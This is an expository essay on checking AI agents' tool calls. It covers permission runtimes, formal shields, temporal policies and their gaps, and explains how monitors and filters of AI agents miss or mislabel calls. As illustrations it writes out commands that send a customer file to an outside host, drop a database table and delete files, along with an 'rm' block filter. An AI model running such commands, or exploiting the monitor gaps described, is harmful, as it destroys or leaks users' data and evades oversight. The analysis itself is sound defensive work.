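# Open-ended tool arguments and the limits of checking what an AI agent does

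## Tool calls, their arguments, and the checks placed on them

An AI agent is a language model that acts through software tools. The model itself only produces text, so to read a file, run a test or send an email, it writes a request in an agreed format. This request is a tool call, and it consists of a tool's name and values for its arguments. A surrounding program, usually called the host or runtime, parses the request, carries it out and passes the result back to the model as text.

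Under the Model Context Protocol, an open standard for connecting models to outside tools, a call to a weather service has the name `get_weather` and the arguments `{"location": "New York"}`. Anthropic's *Bash tool*, the documentation for a tool that gives the Claude models a command shell, has the same structure under slightly different labels:

```
{"name": "bash", "input": {"command": "ls *.py"}}
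```

The command lists the Python files in the current directory. The developer's application receives the record, runs the command in its own shell process, and returns whatever the shell prints. Claude does not run the command itself, so the command can be checked after Claude requests it and before the application runs it.

A tool call's arguments can take far more values than its name. A host can list every tool name at any time, and the Model Context Protocol recommends that each name be unique on its server and at most 128 characters long. Each tool also has a schema that declares its fields and their types. The weather tool's schema requires one string. The shell tool's `command` is also a string, so a type check rejects a missing field or a number but accepts any line that could be typed at a terminal.

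### A release agent

Suppose a software company gives its release work to an agent with four tools:

- `test()` runs a fixed test suite on the current build and reports pass or fail.
- `deploy(version)` puts one of the company's stored builds on the production servers.
- `run_shell(command)` runs a command in a shell session on the build machine.
- `send_message(to, body)` sends text to a person or a mailing list.

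We assume that the agent cannot edit the test suite. If it could, `test()` would run whatever code the agent had put there, and a tool with no arguments would be as hard to check as a shell.

The effects of a tool call are the changes it makes to files, processes, remote systems, or people's beliefs and conduct, and any information it discloses. For example, `deploy("2.4.1")` replaces the program that customers use. An argument's interpreter is whatever turns it into effects, which may be a shell, a language runtime, a remote server, or a human or model that reads a message. The interpreter for `command` is bash, and the interpreter for `body` is the release manager who opens the email. Arguments can be classified by what determines their effects.

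| Kind of argument | Example | What settles the effect |
|---|---|---|
| Choice from a list | `version` in `deploy` | The tool's definition, value by value |
| Number | The amount of a payment | The tool's definition, through one rule for all amounts |
| Reference (path, web address, record number) | `to` in `send_message` | The definition, plus whatever the reference points to at that moment |
| Program | `command` in `run_shell` | The shell and the state of the machine |
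| Message | `body` in `send_message` | The reader |

None of the release agent's tools takes a number, but a running example in Ray's *What Can Be Enforced?* (2026) is an email and payments assistant with a `transfer(to, amount)` tool. Ray models an action as one of finitely many types plus data from a domain that may be infinite. Even this simple assistant can therefore make infinitely many distinct calls, although the effect of any particular transfer is easy to understand.

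What a reference points to can change while the reference stays the same. The Model Context Protocol advises a server that keeps a shopping cart to give the model an identifier, `basket_id`, which is an ordinary string that the model sends back on later calls. The server looks up the cart's contents on each call, so purchases made with the same identifier at different times can be for different goods. Likewise, a message to a customer mailing list goes to whoever is on the list when it is sent. If `deploy` accepted "latest" as a `version`, that argument would become a reference rather than a choice from a list.

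The text of a command can omit nearly everything of interest about its effects, so even a reader who knows bash perfectly may need to see the earlier calls. In an example from Anthropic, Claude installs a library, writes a short Python script to a file, and then issues the command `python fetch_joke.py`. The script contacts a web server, but nothing in the command shows this because the code is in a file that an earlier call created. The shell session also keeps its working directory from one call to the next, so the folder that `rm -r build` deletes depends on where the last `cd` went.

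No specification describes how the recipient of a message will interpret it. "Version 2.4 is safe to install" may lead one customer to upgrade tonight and another to do nothing. If the recipient is an AI agent, it may treat a sentence in the message as an instruction.

`deploy` is a typed tool, meaning its argument has a declared type and the tool's definition specifies what every allowed value does. `command` and `body` are open arguments because the interpreter and the current state, rather than the tool's definition, determine what they do.

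### Between the model and the tool

*Agentao* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) describes a runtime that checks permissions between a model's request for a tool call and the call's execution. When the model proposes one or more calls, the runtime turns each into a standard record and returns malformed ones to the model as errors. It then decides whether to permit each remaining call, executes the permitted ones, and cleans up the output before the model sees it. For each refused call, it also tells the model not to attempt the same thing by other means.

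The decision is a function of four things:

$$D(\text{tool}, \text{argument}, \text{state}, \text{policy}) = \text{ALLOW, PROMPT or DENY}$$

The state is the runtime's state, including the session's mode, and the policy is the set of rules in force. PROMPT means the runtime asks a person. Each rule tests the tool's name, the arguments, and the state, and specifies an outcome; it matches a call when all three tests succeed. The release agent's host might write a rule that matches calls to `deploy` with any version beginning with "3.", in any state, and has the outcome PROMPT. Commercial coding agents apply similar permission rules to shell commands.

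Agentao first denies any call on a hard-coded list of unsafe actions, then any call that could write when the session is in read-only mode, then any call that matches a denial rule for the current run. It then applies the host's own rules, where the first match wins, followed by the rules of the active mode. A careless "allow" from the host therefore takes effect before the mode's more cautious rules are checked. If nothing matches, the runtime asks for confirmation when the tool is flagged as requiring it and otherwise allows the call.

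*LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) uses the opposite default. Its guard checks calls against policies written in the proof language Lean and blocks any call that no permit covers. The choice of default hardly matters for `deploy`, which has only a few dozen versions, because a careful author can write a rule for each. But no author can foresee every `command`, so the default will apply in a large share of cases.

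*Guardrails as Infrastructure* (2026) adds a fourth outcome, in which the runtime rewrites the arguments before execution, and Ray allows a gate to substitute a different action. Asking a person works only if someone is there to answer. In one case that Jin and colleagues discuss, a scheduler produces a digest overnight, so the host has to decide in advance what the agent may do.

In another of their cases, a rule checks only one field of a tool call. A customer-support agent can call a tool named SendReply, and the policy allows the call only if its `confidence` field is at least 0.9. But the model chooses that number itself, and the rule doesn't check the text the customer will read. Sankar and colleagues guard against this kind of problem by treating the whole call as untrusted and taking the facts from the application's own database. If an agent claims that a customer has given approval,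 the claim has no effect unless the system has a record of it.

Labels on tools are not enough to check what a call will do. The Model Context Protocol lets a server mark a tool as read-only or destructive, but these marks are only hints, and under the standard clients should never base decisions on them when the server is untrusted. Even an accurate label applies to the whole tool, so `run_shell` has the same label whether it lists a directory or erases it. Jin and colleagues concede that their own runtime offers no formal guarantee of safety and cannot infer what every external tool will do.

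### What it would mean for a check to give a guarantee

An effect bound guarantees that every call a check allows has only effects within a stated set. For the release agent, a useful bound would be that no `run_shell` call deletes a file. A syntactic check evaluates a call using only the argument's text and a fixed policy, without running the argument or looking at the state. It is Agentao's function $D$ without the state. This definition includes a filter that refuses any `command` containing the letters "rm", but excludes a guard that consults a database before deciding.

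A check is sound if it never admits a call whose effects fall outside the stated set. Write $E(c, s)$ for the effects of call $c$ in state $s$, and $B$ for the stated set. A syntactic check $C$ is sound for $B$ when

$$C(c) = \text{ALLOW} \;\Rightarrow\; E(c, s) \subseteq B \quad \text{for every state } s \text{ that can arise.}$$

The last clause carries much of the difficulty. The check does not see which state the call will run in, so its promise has to hold in all of them. (A call that goes to a person counts as not admitted here, since whatever follows rests on the person's judgement.)

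The "rm" filter is unsound for the bound on deletion, because `find . -delete` contains no "rm" and deletes every file it can reach. The filter also refuses the harmless command `ls formats`. This is annoying but doesn't affect soundness, since even a check that refused every command would be sound, though useless. A sound check is easy to write for `deploy`. If the check admits only "2.4.1" and "2.4.2", no admitted call can put any other build into production, provided the company never reuses a version number.

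Anthropic publishes a more careful filter as sample code. It allows a command only if the first word is one of nine, including `ls`, `cat`, `grep` and `find`, and it rejects shell operators, such as the pipe, that stand as separate words. `cat data.txt|grep x` still gets through because the filter splits the text at spaces and doesn't detect a pipe without spaces around it. `find . -delete` also gets through because `find` is on the list and the command contains no operator. Anthropic describes the code as a tripwire for obvious mistakes and recommends a container or virtual machine as the real control.

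Sankar and colleagues wrote contracts for 199 tools in DTap, a benchmark of attacks on agents, including tools that read a record or place a trade. Each contract fixes the tool's argument schema and the resources a call can affect. Where they could not model a tool's effect, as with general shell commands, their guard stops the call. Calls to such tools made up 13% of those it stopped during attacks. Their guarantee holds only if the guard's observations match the real environment and every call that matters passes through the guard.

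### Rules about a whole run

Many rules concern a sequence of calls. "Do not deploy a build until `test()` has passed on it" is one. Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), worked out which rules a monitor can enforce if all it can do is watch a run step by step and halt it before a violation. Any such rule must be a safety property, meaning that a run which breaks the rule has already broken it after finitely many steps, and nothing later can repair the breach. In Ray's notation, where $P$ is the set of permitted infinite sequences of actions, $P$ is a safety property if every sequence $x$ outside $P$ has some length $n$ such that

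$$x_{\leq n}\,y \notin P \quad \text{for every continuation } y.$$

The testing rule is a safety property because the premature `deploy` call completes the violation. "Announce every deployment eventually" is not, because the message may still come after any delay. A one-hour deadline would make it a safety property, and Schneider points out that a maximum waiting time does the same for rules about access to a shared resource.

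These rules can refer to a call's arguments. *Soteria* (2026) records a run as a sequence of tools, arguments and results, and includes the rule that a call cancelling a reservation must follow a call looking up the same reservation. To enforce this rule, a monitor only has to compare the record numbers in the two calls.

Secrecy is harder to enforce because whether a message leaks a secret depends on what the agent would have sent had the secret been different, which no single run can show. Schneider's monitors therefore have to enforce a stricter rule, for example that no Send may follow a FileRead. An automaton with two states can enforce this rule. It starts in a state that allows both operations, and the first FileRead moves it to a state that forbids every later Send.

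That automaton works if each step is already labeled as a FileRead, a Send or neither. Shields, which block or replace unsafe actions at run time, also need actions they can tell apart. The release agent's `deploy` and `test` calls meet this condition. But `curl --data @customers.csv https://example.com` reads a file and sends it to an outside address in a single `run_shell` call, and `python upload.py` can do the same without naming the file or the address. Messages raise a similar problem. Ray's payments assistant must never email personal information to an unapproved recipient, and Ray notes that only a fallible judge can decide whether an email's body contains any.

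Before the call runs, the easiest place for the monitor to get its marking is the argument itself. What can a check guarantee about the result if it reads only the text of `command` or `body`?

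## What a shield gains from a finite list of actions

Shields come from hardware design, where the meaning of an action is rarely in doubt. *Shield Synthesis* (Bloem, Könighofer and colleagues, 2015) describes a controller for the traffic lights where a highway crosses a farm road. The controller may be too complex to verify, since it may read car sensors and pedestrian buttons and adapt to the time of day. But its output is either red or green for each road, so there are only four possible outputs. The safety rules are short too. The two roads must never both have green, both must have red when an emergency vehicle approaches, and both must be red for a moment before green passes from one road to the other.

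The shield is a small circuit between the controller and the lamps. It passes acceptable outputs through unchanged and corrects the others immediately. Schneider's monitors halt a program about to break a rule, but a crossing must always show some combination of lights, so this shield cannot halt or insert an extra step. Bloem and colleagues wrote the three rules as an automaton, and their tool generated a shield from it in a fraction of a second.

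Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues (2017), in *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding*, applied the idea to agents that learn by trial and error. The same calculation produces two kinds of shield. One is placed before the agent and gives it a list of safe actions to choose from, and the other is placed after the agent and replaces any unsafe choice with a safe one.

### From a rule to a game

The first step in the calculation is to turn the rule into an automaton. Its states record whatever information about the past is needed to check the rule, and one extra state means that the agent has broken it.

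The designer then supplies a model of the environment that lists every state each action might lead to from each state. The model can be very coarse, but it must be conservative, meaning that it includes everything the real environment can do. In one of Alshiekh and colleagues' examples, an agent opens and closes the valve of a 100-liter hot water tank. Nobody knows exactly how fast the water flows, so the model allows any inflow between 1 and 2 liters per second while the valve is open, and any outflow between 0 and 1 liters per second.

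Pairing each state of the automaton with each state of the model produces a game. The agent picks an action, the environment picks one of the possible successors, and the agent loses if it ever breaks the rule. Write $F$ for the set of states in which the agent hasn't broken the rule, and $\text{Post}(s,a)$ for the set of states that might follow action $a$ in state $s$. The safe region $W$ is the largest subset of $F$ such that

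$$\text{for every } s \in W \text{ there is an action } a \text{ with } \text{Post}(s,a) \subseteq W.$$

To find $W$, start with all of $F$ and remove any state in which every action might lead outside the set. Removing a state can make others unsafe, so repeat until nothing changes. According to Könighofer, Bloem and colleagues (2025), in *Shields for Safe Reinforcement Learning*, this takes time proportional to the size of the game, and the best current methods can handle environments with billions of states. The shield then permits

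$$\text{Permitted}(s) = \{\,a : \text{Post}(s,a) \subseteq W\,\}.$$

Because $W$ accounts for later steps, the shield can block an action long before any harm occurs. Once the tank's valve opens, it must stay open for at least three seconds, which could add 6 liters. The level must stay below 100 liters, so the shield blocks opening the valve when the level is above 93.

Alshiekh and colleagues proved that an agent with such a shield never gets stuck, because every state in $W$ has at least one permitted action, and never breaks the rule as long as the environment behaves as modeled. They also proved that the shield interferes as little as possible, so if it seems too cautious, the fault is in the model. The shield blocks an action only if, in some environment consistent with the model and with everything observed so far, that action could lead to a violation that nothing the agent did later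 would be sure to prevent.

### A shield for the release agent

Suppose the release agent has only four actions. `edit` changes the code, `test` runs the test suite, `deploy` puts the current code on the production servers, and `wait` does nothing. The agent may deploy only tested code, and code counts as tested if it has passed the suite since the last edit.

The automaton for this rule has three states: "tested", "untested" and "untested code deployed". The only uncertainty in the environment is whether untested code will pass. We assume code that has passed once would pass again. The model therefore needs no states of its own, and the game has the same three states as the automaton.

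| State | After `edit` | After `test` | After `deploy` | After `wait` | Permitted actions |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tested | Untested | Tested | Tested | Tested | `edit`, `test`, `deploy`, `wait` |
| Untested | Untested | Tested or untested | Untested code deployed | Untested | `edit`, `test`, `wait` |
| Untested code deployed | No change | No change | No change | No change | None |

The search for the safe region $W$ starts with the states "tested" and "untested". The agent can stay in either state by waiting, so both remain in $W$. The shield blocks only `deploy` when the code is untested. If the agent tries it, a shield placed after the agent could run `test` instead.

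Suppose a colleague sets up a scheduled job that may deploy the current code at any moment. If the code is untested, the job might deploy it before the agent's next action takes effect, so "untested" is no longer in the safe region $W$. "Tested" remains in $W$ because waiting keeps the code tested. But `edit` now leads out of $W$, so the shield blocks every edit, even though editing deploys nothing. If the code is untested at the start, no action is safe and no shield exists. The company would have to pause the job before the agent could do any work.

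### Four premises

The release agent's shield depends on four premises:

1. Someone can list all the actions.
2. For each action in each state, the model includes every state that might follow.
3. Each call that the agent makes corresponds to exactly one action on the list, and the shield can tell which one.
4. In every state the agent can reach under the shield, there is a safe action to use in place of an unsafe one.

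Alshiekh and colleagues say explicitly that a shield needs a model, and Könighofer and colleagues stress that a shield's guarantees are "always relative to the world model". Both also discuss safe replacements. Könighofer and colleagues suggest, for example, that a drone outside the safe region use a fixed fallback such as landing.

The correspondence between calls and actions gets much less attention. Alshiekh and colleagues don't list it as an assumption, and in their setting they hardly need to, because an agent's choice between "open" and "close" already identifies the action for the shield. The function that maps a concrete call to the symbol a rule uses is called an abstraction map, and it is trivial for a valve or a traffic light.

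### A shell in place of the four actions

Suppose we replace the agent's four actions with a single action, `run_shell(command)`. The agent can still edit a file with `sed`, test with `pytest`, deploy with `./deploy.sh` and wait with `sleep 60`.

The most obvious loss is the list of actions, but this does little harm by itself. If the host limits commands to 200 characters, a finite list still exists, with more than $10^{395}$ entries. The shield could use the same three-state table as before if a perfect labeler could tell whether each command edits, tests, deploys or does nothing relevant. Researchers have also built shields for data with infinitely many values, such as numbers, where one rule covers all the values.

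No real labeler is perfect. `make release` may deploy the code or only package it, depending on the Makefile, and for a language as rich as the shell's, no algorithm can label every command correctly from its text. Some commands also have no single correct label, because one call can perform two actions and the shield needs their order to apply the rule. If the code is tested, a command that deploys it and then edits it follows the rule, but one that edits it and then deploys it breaks the rule.

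Without a label, the shield must rely on its model of what an unknown command might do. A cautious model over-approximates by assuming that each command could have any effect. Any command might then edit the code and deploy it, so `run_shell` can lead to "untested code deployed" from every state. The only safe option is to refuse the call, which amounts to waiting. This shield is sound, but it blocks every command, including `ls`. By the result on minimal interference, no better shield exists for this model.

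The optimistic choice is to treat any unrecognized command as harmless. The shield then permits `make release` when the code is untested. The calculation still produces a shield and a proof, but the proof covers only environments that match the model. In Alshiekh and colleagues' construction, a run that departs from the model counts as a win for the agent, so the shield need not keep that run safe. Probabilities don't solve the problem either. Könighofer and colleagues describe shields that block an action only if the risk of harm within a fixed number of steps is too high, but calculating that risk requires knowing how likely an arbitrary command is to deploy something.

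Even a correct label can leave the successor states unknown. Suppose the labeler correctly marks a command as `edit`, and the command changes `deploy.sh`. The next deployment may then do something different from the last one, but the three-state model cannot record this. We could add the contents of `deploy.sh` to the state, but we would also have to add the test suite, the Makefile, and every other file that the agent can write and a later command can run.

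A finite list doesn't fix any of this. For example, a tool `run_script(n)` might run one of ten scripts on the build machine, and the agent might be able to edit those scripts. The agent can make only ten different calls, but a shield can't predict their effects any better than it can predict those of shell commands. The same is true of `test()` if the agent can edit the test suite. So a shield needs an accurate map and model even when the list is short, and if it has them, the list doesn't have to be short. Finite lists work well in hardware because whoever writes the list generally knows what each entry does.

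The need for a safe replacement causes less trouble for software agents. A shield can usually just refuse an agent's call, which it can't do with a traffic light. Refusing fails when doing nothing is dangerous, as with the scheduled job, or when an earlier command has left a server half-configured.

Finding a replacement that serves the agent's purpose is harder. When a traffic controller makes a mistake, Bloem and colleagues' shield tracks the states that every correct output would have led to. That works with four outputs, but for a shell command, the shield would have to guess which of an enormous number of other commands the agent might have meant.

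### Rules about tool names

A checker can keep its list of actions finite by ignoring tool arguments altogether. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) does this for agents whose steps the developers have laid out as a graph. Each node is a step, such as a tool call, a call to a language model, or a human approval, and the edges show which steps can follow which. Agentproof extracts the graph automatically from four popular frameworks for building agents and checks it before the agent runs.

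Its temporal rules take seven forms. `G !tool:drop_table` bans a tool, and `tool:fetch_pii -> F[<=3] tool:anonymize` requires a call to `anonymize` within three steps of fetching personal information. The other forms cover responses with no fixed deadline, chains of responses, conditions that must hold until some event, and combinations of rules with "and" or "or". Each rule compiles to a finite automaton, which is usually tiny. A ban, for example, needs only two states.

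Agentproof then pairs the automaton with the graph, much as a shield pairs its rule with a model of the environment. It searches for any path on which the rule fails, whereas a shield looks for safe choices. The search includes paths the real agent would never take, so it can raise false alarms. If it finds no violation, no run of the graph breaks the rule as the automaton encodes it, provided the extracted graph is accurate and doesn't change during the run.

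Xavier and colleagues tested this on 18 workflows they wrote themselves with deliberate defects, so the results measure what the tool can detect rather than how common the defects are. Five workflows had structural faults, such as a step with no way forward, and ten had no human approval step. The team also checked 15 temporal rules. In one workflow, the search found a path with no human review after the agent drafted an email, which ten random runs had missed. The largest search covered only 24 combined states. On an artificial graph with 5,000 nodes, the structural checks took about a tenth of a second.

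These rules can guarantee that certain steps occur, that they occur in a certain order, and that the agent never calls a certain tool. But it's easy to write a rule that guarantees less than its author intended. Xavier and colleagues give `tool:deploy -> F tool:approve` as a rule for approving deployments. It requires approval after a deployment rather than before it. The automaton reports a violation only if a second deployment arrives before the first is approved, so an agent that deploys once and never gets approval passes the check.

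A separate check does guarantee approval beforehand. It deletes every human step from the graph and tests whether the agent can still reach `deploy`. If it can't, every path to `deploy` goes through a person. But that person may have approved an earlier version of the code, because the check doesn't require a new approval after each edit. The release agent's rule also has no direct equivalent among the seven forms, because the language has no operators for past events.

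The bigger limitation is that the rules match only a tool's name, an action type, a decision or a tag, never an argument. A call to `run_shell` therefore produces the same symbol, `tool:run_shell`, whatever the command is. The ban on `drop_table` stops the agent from calling a tool with that name, but not from running a shell command such as `psql -c "DROP TABLE customers"`, which deletes the same data. Banning `run_shell` would close this gap but would also block every useful command. Requiring approval before each call would guarantee that a person is asked, but not that the command is safe.

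Even the symbols Agentproof does use can be wrong. In one of the four frameworks, it recognizes a human approval step by looking for the word "human" in the step's name. If a developer names the step `manager_review`, Agentproof classifies it as a call to a language model.

### Where shields for language models get their symbols

Several recent systems apply shields or similar monitors to language-model agents and take tool arguments into account. *MENTOR* (Anand, Chatzi and colleagues, 2026) is the closest to the classical construction. It is designed for agents that follow written procedures, such as a company's rules for booking travel. Before the agent starts work, language models translate the procedures into temporal rules. MENTOR then turns these rules into a game and calculates which tools are unsafe at each point and which would make progress on the task.

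The game uses only tool names. A constraint solver, which can handle text and whole numbers without trying every value, checks the arguments separately. In the travel example, the agent must check the distance before it books anything. After that, the game permits `book_flight`, but the solver rejects a business-class ticket unless the trip is urgent and there are no economy seats.

MENTOR can also block unsafe calls as the model writes them if it has access to the model's probabilities for each token, or small piece of text. It gives zero probability to any token that can lead only to unsafe tool names. This works because the names form a short list. For arguments, MENTOR blocks only values it has already identified as unsafe, and it checks the completed call again because two values that are acceptable separately can be unacceptable together.

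Many of the facts these checks need are written in ordinary prose. Another language model, the labeler, reads the user's request and records, for example, that the trip is from Toronto to Chicago and isn't urgent. It also reads written results from tools and gives each one a label from a short list, such as "500 km or more". The game and the solver then treat these labels as facts. If the labeler marks a 450-kilometer trip as "500 km or more", the shield will permit a flight that the manual forbids, even though every formal step worked correctly.

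Anand and colleagues measured how often an agent completed a task correctly in all five attempts. For GPT-5.4 mini, the shield raised this rate from 62% to 77% on a set of operational procedures and from 21% to 40% on a set of retail procedures. Even with the shield, most retail tasks failed at least once. Agents under other guards often repeated a blocked call because those guards offered no alternative, while MENTOR suggests a permitted call. The quality of the labeler also mattered, and open-weight models labeled poorly until the researchers trained one for the job.

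Other systems get their symbols in different ways. *VIGIL* (2026) describes a monitor that records a run as a series of typed events and uses a constraint solver for each decision. *Multi-Aspect Runtime Verification for Simulation-Based V&V of LLM-Enabled Autonomous Agents* (2026) describes a system that attaches a set of labels to each call, along with the tool's name and typed arguments, and tries the call on a copy of its world model first. All the facts that a call produces share one point in time, so a call that produces many facts still counts as one step toward a deadline. But those facts then have no order, so if a single call both edits and deploys, they don't show which happened first.

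AgentSpec, which Anand and colleagues used for comparison, labels events with fixed keywords and handwritten text patterns. This is predictable, but on shell commands it would have the same weakness as the filter for "rm". Some systems use a model's judgment instead. *Sapien* (2026) extends regular expressions to compare values across calls, and sends plain-language conditions to a language-model classifier. In *ShieldAgent* (2025), the guard decides which facts hold by searching the agent's history, answering yes-or-no questions, and calling content-moderation services, before it verifies the rules formally. Both systems can apply exact logic, but they apply it to a model's best guess about the facts.

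Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, point out that existing monitors for agents assume structured calls with known meanings, which shell commands don't have. Their system labels a command by what it does rather than by its text. It runs the command in a disposable copy of the file system, holds back any network requests, and tracks the program's requests to the operating system. It then translates those system requests into a sequence of abstract actions of eleven kinds, including `read`, `copy` and `uploadNet`. This restores a finite set of action types, but only after the command has run.

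In their example, an agent uploads a harmless report with `curl`, copies a confidential inventory over the report, and then runs the same `curl` command again. Both uploads produce the same abstract action, but Tether allows the first and blocks the second because it has recorded that the file now holds confidential data. However, Tether can't always track exactly where data went. If a script reads one file and then writes to another, Tether treats the data as having moved between them, even if it didn't.

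## Arguments with infinitely many values that can still be checked

The payments assistant described earlier can make infinitely many different `transfer(to, amount)` calls, because an amount can be any positive whole number. But if a rule allows at most 100 dollars per transfer, a single comparison shows whether a call is allowed. The check is also sound, because the tool's definition fixes how much money each call moves. No allowed call moves more than 100 dollars, whatever state the bank's systems are in.

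The rule relies on the declared type excluding negative amounts. If the tool accepted them, the rule would allow a transfer of −5,000 dollars, which might take money from the recipient.

An argument can take infinitely many values and still be checkable. `transfer` is checkable because one known rule gives the effect of every amount, and because the bound on effects translates into a condition on the amount that a program can always decide.

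### Shields that handle numbers

Checking a spending limit takes only a comparison, but a shield also has to consider later steps. Designers usually write its rules in linear temporal logic (LTL), which combines statements that are true or false at each step, such as "the valve is open", with operators such as "next" and "always". LTL modulo theories replaces those statements with formulas from a mathematical theory. If the theory is linear arithmetic over the whole numbers, a rule can contain $x < 10$ or $y \le x$.

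Rodríguez, Amir and colleagues (2024), in *Shield Synthesis for LTL Modulo Theories*, showed how to build shields for such rules. In their running example, the environment picks a whole number $x$ at each step and the agent answers with a whole number $y$:

$$\Box\big[\,(x < 10 \to \bigcirc (y > 9))\ \land\ (x \ge 10 \to y \le x)\,\big]$$

The square means "at every step" and the circle means "at the next step". Suppose $x$ is a supplier's stock each day and $y$ is the number of units the agent orders. If stock is below 10, the agent must order at least 10 units the next day. If stock is 10 or more, the agent can't order more than the supplier has.

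There are infinitely many pairs of stock $x$ and order $y$, but the rule depends on only three facts: whether $x$ is below 10, whether $y$ is above 9, and whether $y$ is at most $x$. The method replaces each fact with a true-or-false variable. These variables aren't independent. For example, when stock is 9, an order above 9 can't also be at most $x$. A solver therefore works out which combinations of true and false the agent can bring about at each level of stock.

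| Stock $x$ | $y \le 9$ and $y \le x$ | $y \le 9$ and $y > x$ | $y \ge 10$ and $y \le x$ | $y \ge 10$ and $y > x$ |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 8 or less | Possible | Possible | Impossible | Possible |
| 9 | Possible | Impossible | Impossible | Possible |
| 10 or more | Possible | Impossible | Possible | Possible |

All stock levels fall into three classes, and in each class the agent can choose from two or three kinds of order. This gives a finite game like those used to build ordinary shields. The game needs only two states, depending on whether yesterday's stock was below 10. Both are safe because an order of exactly 10 units satisfies the rule every day.

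Suppose stock is 5 on Monday and 10 on Tuesday, and on Tuesday the agent tries to order 11 units. The shield places the stock in the class "10 or more" and the order in the last column of the table. The game rules out that combination because the order exceeds the stock. It permits only orders of at least 10 and at most the stock, $x$, so the shield uses the solver to find such a number, which here is 10. If several numbers qualify, the designers can have the solver return the one closest to the agent's choice.

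Rodríguez and colleagues proved that any agent combined with such a shield obeys the rule. Constructing the shield requires a theory in which a solver can always decide whether formulas of the form "there are values such that, for all other values, ..." are true. Linear arithmetic over the whole numbers is one such theory. "This command deletes no files" is not a formula in any such theory, so the method doesn't apply to `run_shell`.

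The shield can also interfere more than it has to. The agent has fewer options with a stock of 9 than with any lower stock, so designers can save work by treating every low-stock day as if the stock were 9. The guarantee still holds, but the shield now overrides a harmless order of 2 units when the stock is 0.

Each formula in this logic compares numbers from the same step, so it can't, for example, add up a month of payments unless another component supplies the running total as an input.

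### When no shield exists

A small change to the rule can make it impossible to enforce. Rodríguez, Shaik and colleagues (2025), in *Explanations for Unrealizability of Infinite-State Safety Shields*, give this example:

$$\Box\big[\,(x < 2 \to \bigcirc (y > 1))\ \land\ (x \ge 2 \to y < x)\,\big]$$

Suppose an agent orders whole units from a supplier each day under two rules. If the supplier's stock is below 2, the agent must order more than 1 unit the next day. If the stock is 2 or more, that day's order must be less than the stock. When the stock is 1 on Monday and 2 on Tuesday, Tuesday's order must be more than 1 and less than 2. No whole number fits, so no shield can guarantee that the agent follows both rules. If the agent could order fractions, as with liters of fuel, ordering 1.5 every day would always satisfy both rules, and a shield would exist.

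To find such contradictions, the method writes out the rule for a fixed number of days and uses a solver to check whether some sequence of stock levels leaves no sequence of orders that satisfies the rule. One day is too short to produce a contradiction here, but with two days the solver returns the sequence 1, 2, which a policy author can easily understand. Some rules are harder to explain. In another example, the environment can force a violation in four steps with a fixed sequence, or in two if it sees the agent's first answer before choosing its second number.

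These contradictions arise only when the agent has to do something, in this case order a certain quantity. Most policies for software agents only forbid calls, so an agent that makes no calls can't break them. Under such a policy, a runtime can always refuse calls without first solving a game.

### Rules for single calls and for histories

Cedar is an open-source language for policies that permit or forbid a request. Amazon Web Services' *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* describes how the company uses Cedar at a gateway between agents and their tools. The gateway generates a schema from the tools' descriptions, so a policy can refer to each argument by name and type. It blocks a call unless a policy permits it and none forbids it.

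One example policy permits a bulk discount if the customer has platinum status and the order is for at least 50 items, except for limited-edition or seasonal products. The customer's status comes from a login token that the model can't alter. The model supplies the quantity and could enter any number, but any number can be checked against the 50-item minimum.

Cedar has no loops and no memory of earlier requests, which makes it less expressive but lets a solver translate a whole set of policies into formulas and prove things about them. Suppose a policy permits discounts on orders of at least 50 items unless the product is a limited edition, and someone changes the exception to cover only limited-edition orders of more than 200 items. The solver reports that the policy has become more permissive, even though the added condition looks like a restriction, because an order of 73 limited-edition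 items now gets the discount.

Such a proof covers the policy and assumes that the tool behaves as expected. A 500-dollar limit on `refundAmount` caps a refund only if the tool pays out the amount in that field. Cedar also evaluates each call separately, so an agent can make ten refunds of 499 dollars without breaking the limit.

AWS built Dogwood, an extension of Cedar, for rules about earlier calls. AWS's *Temporal policies* explains that the gateway records each session's requests and results, and a policy can search this record within a time window. One of the examples in AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* allows a transfer only to an account that the agent has looked up in the past hour. Its central condition, slightly shortened, is:

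```
formerly within 1h get_account_balance::response {
  output.accountId: context.input.toAccount
}
```

The gateway compares the account number in the new call with the numbers that earlier lookups returned. The number of possible account numbers is unlimited, but the gateway only has to test whether two strings are equal, not interpret them. The rule stops the agent from inventing an account, but the agent can still look up the wrong customer and then pay them.

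Strictly, this is no longer a syntactic check, because the decision depends on a record of past events as well as the call's text. The check can also fail if it adds up the wrong events. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* relays a warning from AWS about a policy that caps total transfers at 5,000 dollars. If the policy adds up only completed transfers, an agent can send three transfers of 2,000 dollars at once, and all three pass because none has finished yet. A policy that adds up requested transfers blocks the third.

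AWS also gives a policy for single-use approvals. It checks that no transfer has completed since the latest approval. By the same reasoning, two transfers sent together could both use one approval.

The caller also chooses the session's identifier, so it can reset every count by starting a new session. AWS says that a limit on the number of calls is not a security control against a determined caller. Dogwood also loses some of what Cedar was designed for. InfoQ reports that Cedar's formal analysis tools don't work on temporal conditions.

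### Rules written for one task

Cedar and Dogwood policies usually stay in force for a long time, but the right limit can depend on the request. An assistant that summarizes an inbox should never send money, but one that the user has told to "refund the person who sent me money last week" has to send it. *Sapien* has a language model write a new policy for each task. The model's only inputs are the user's request and the tools' documentation, so a malicious email can't influence the rules.

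A policy is a regular expression over tool calls, with operators for sequence, choice, repetition and interleaving. A call can also store its arguments and result in a variable that later conditions use. For the refund, a policy might be:

```
list_transactions@past .
send_money(recipient=PREDICATE(paid_me_last_week),
           amount=PREDICATE(matches_payment))
```

The dot means "followed by", and `@past` stores the transaction list. Each predicate is a short Python function that compares the proposed value with that list. Without this comparison, the policy would have to allow any recipient and any amount, because nobody knows the right values until the agent has read the list.

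For some requests, the necessary steps aren't known in advance. If the user writes "do the tasks on my to-do list", the policy allows the agent to fetch the list and leaves a hole for the remaining steps. Once the list arrives, the model writes another policy to fill the hole. This follows the user's wishes, but it also lets anyone who can edit the list influence the policy.

Other conditions concern the meaning of a text, such as whether an email accurately summarizes a document. For these, the policy can use a language model to answer a yes-or-no question. If the model answers wrongly, the policy's other conditions still apply. An attacker who fools the model may get the agent to send a bad summary, but only to the recipient the policy specifies.

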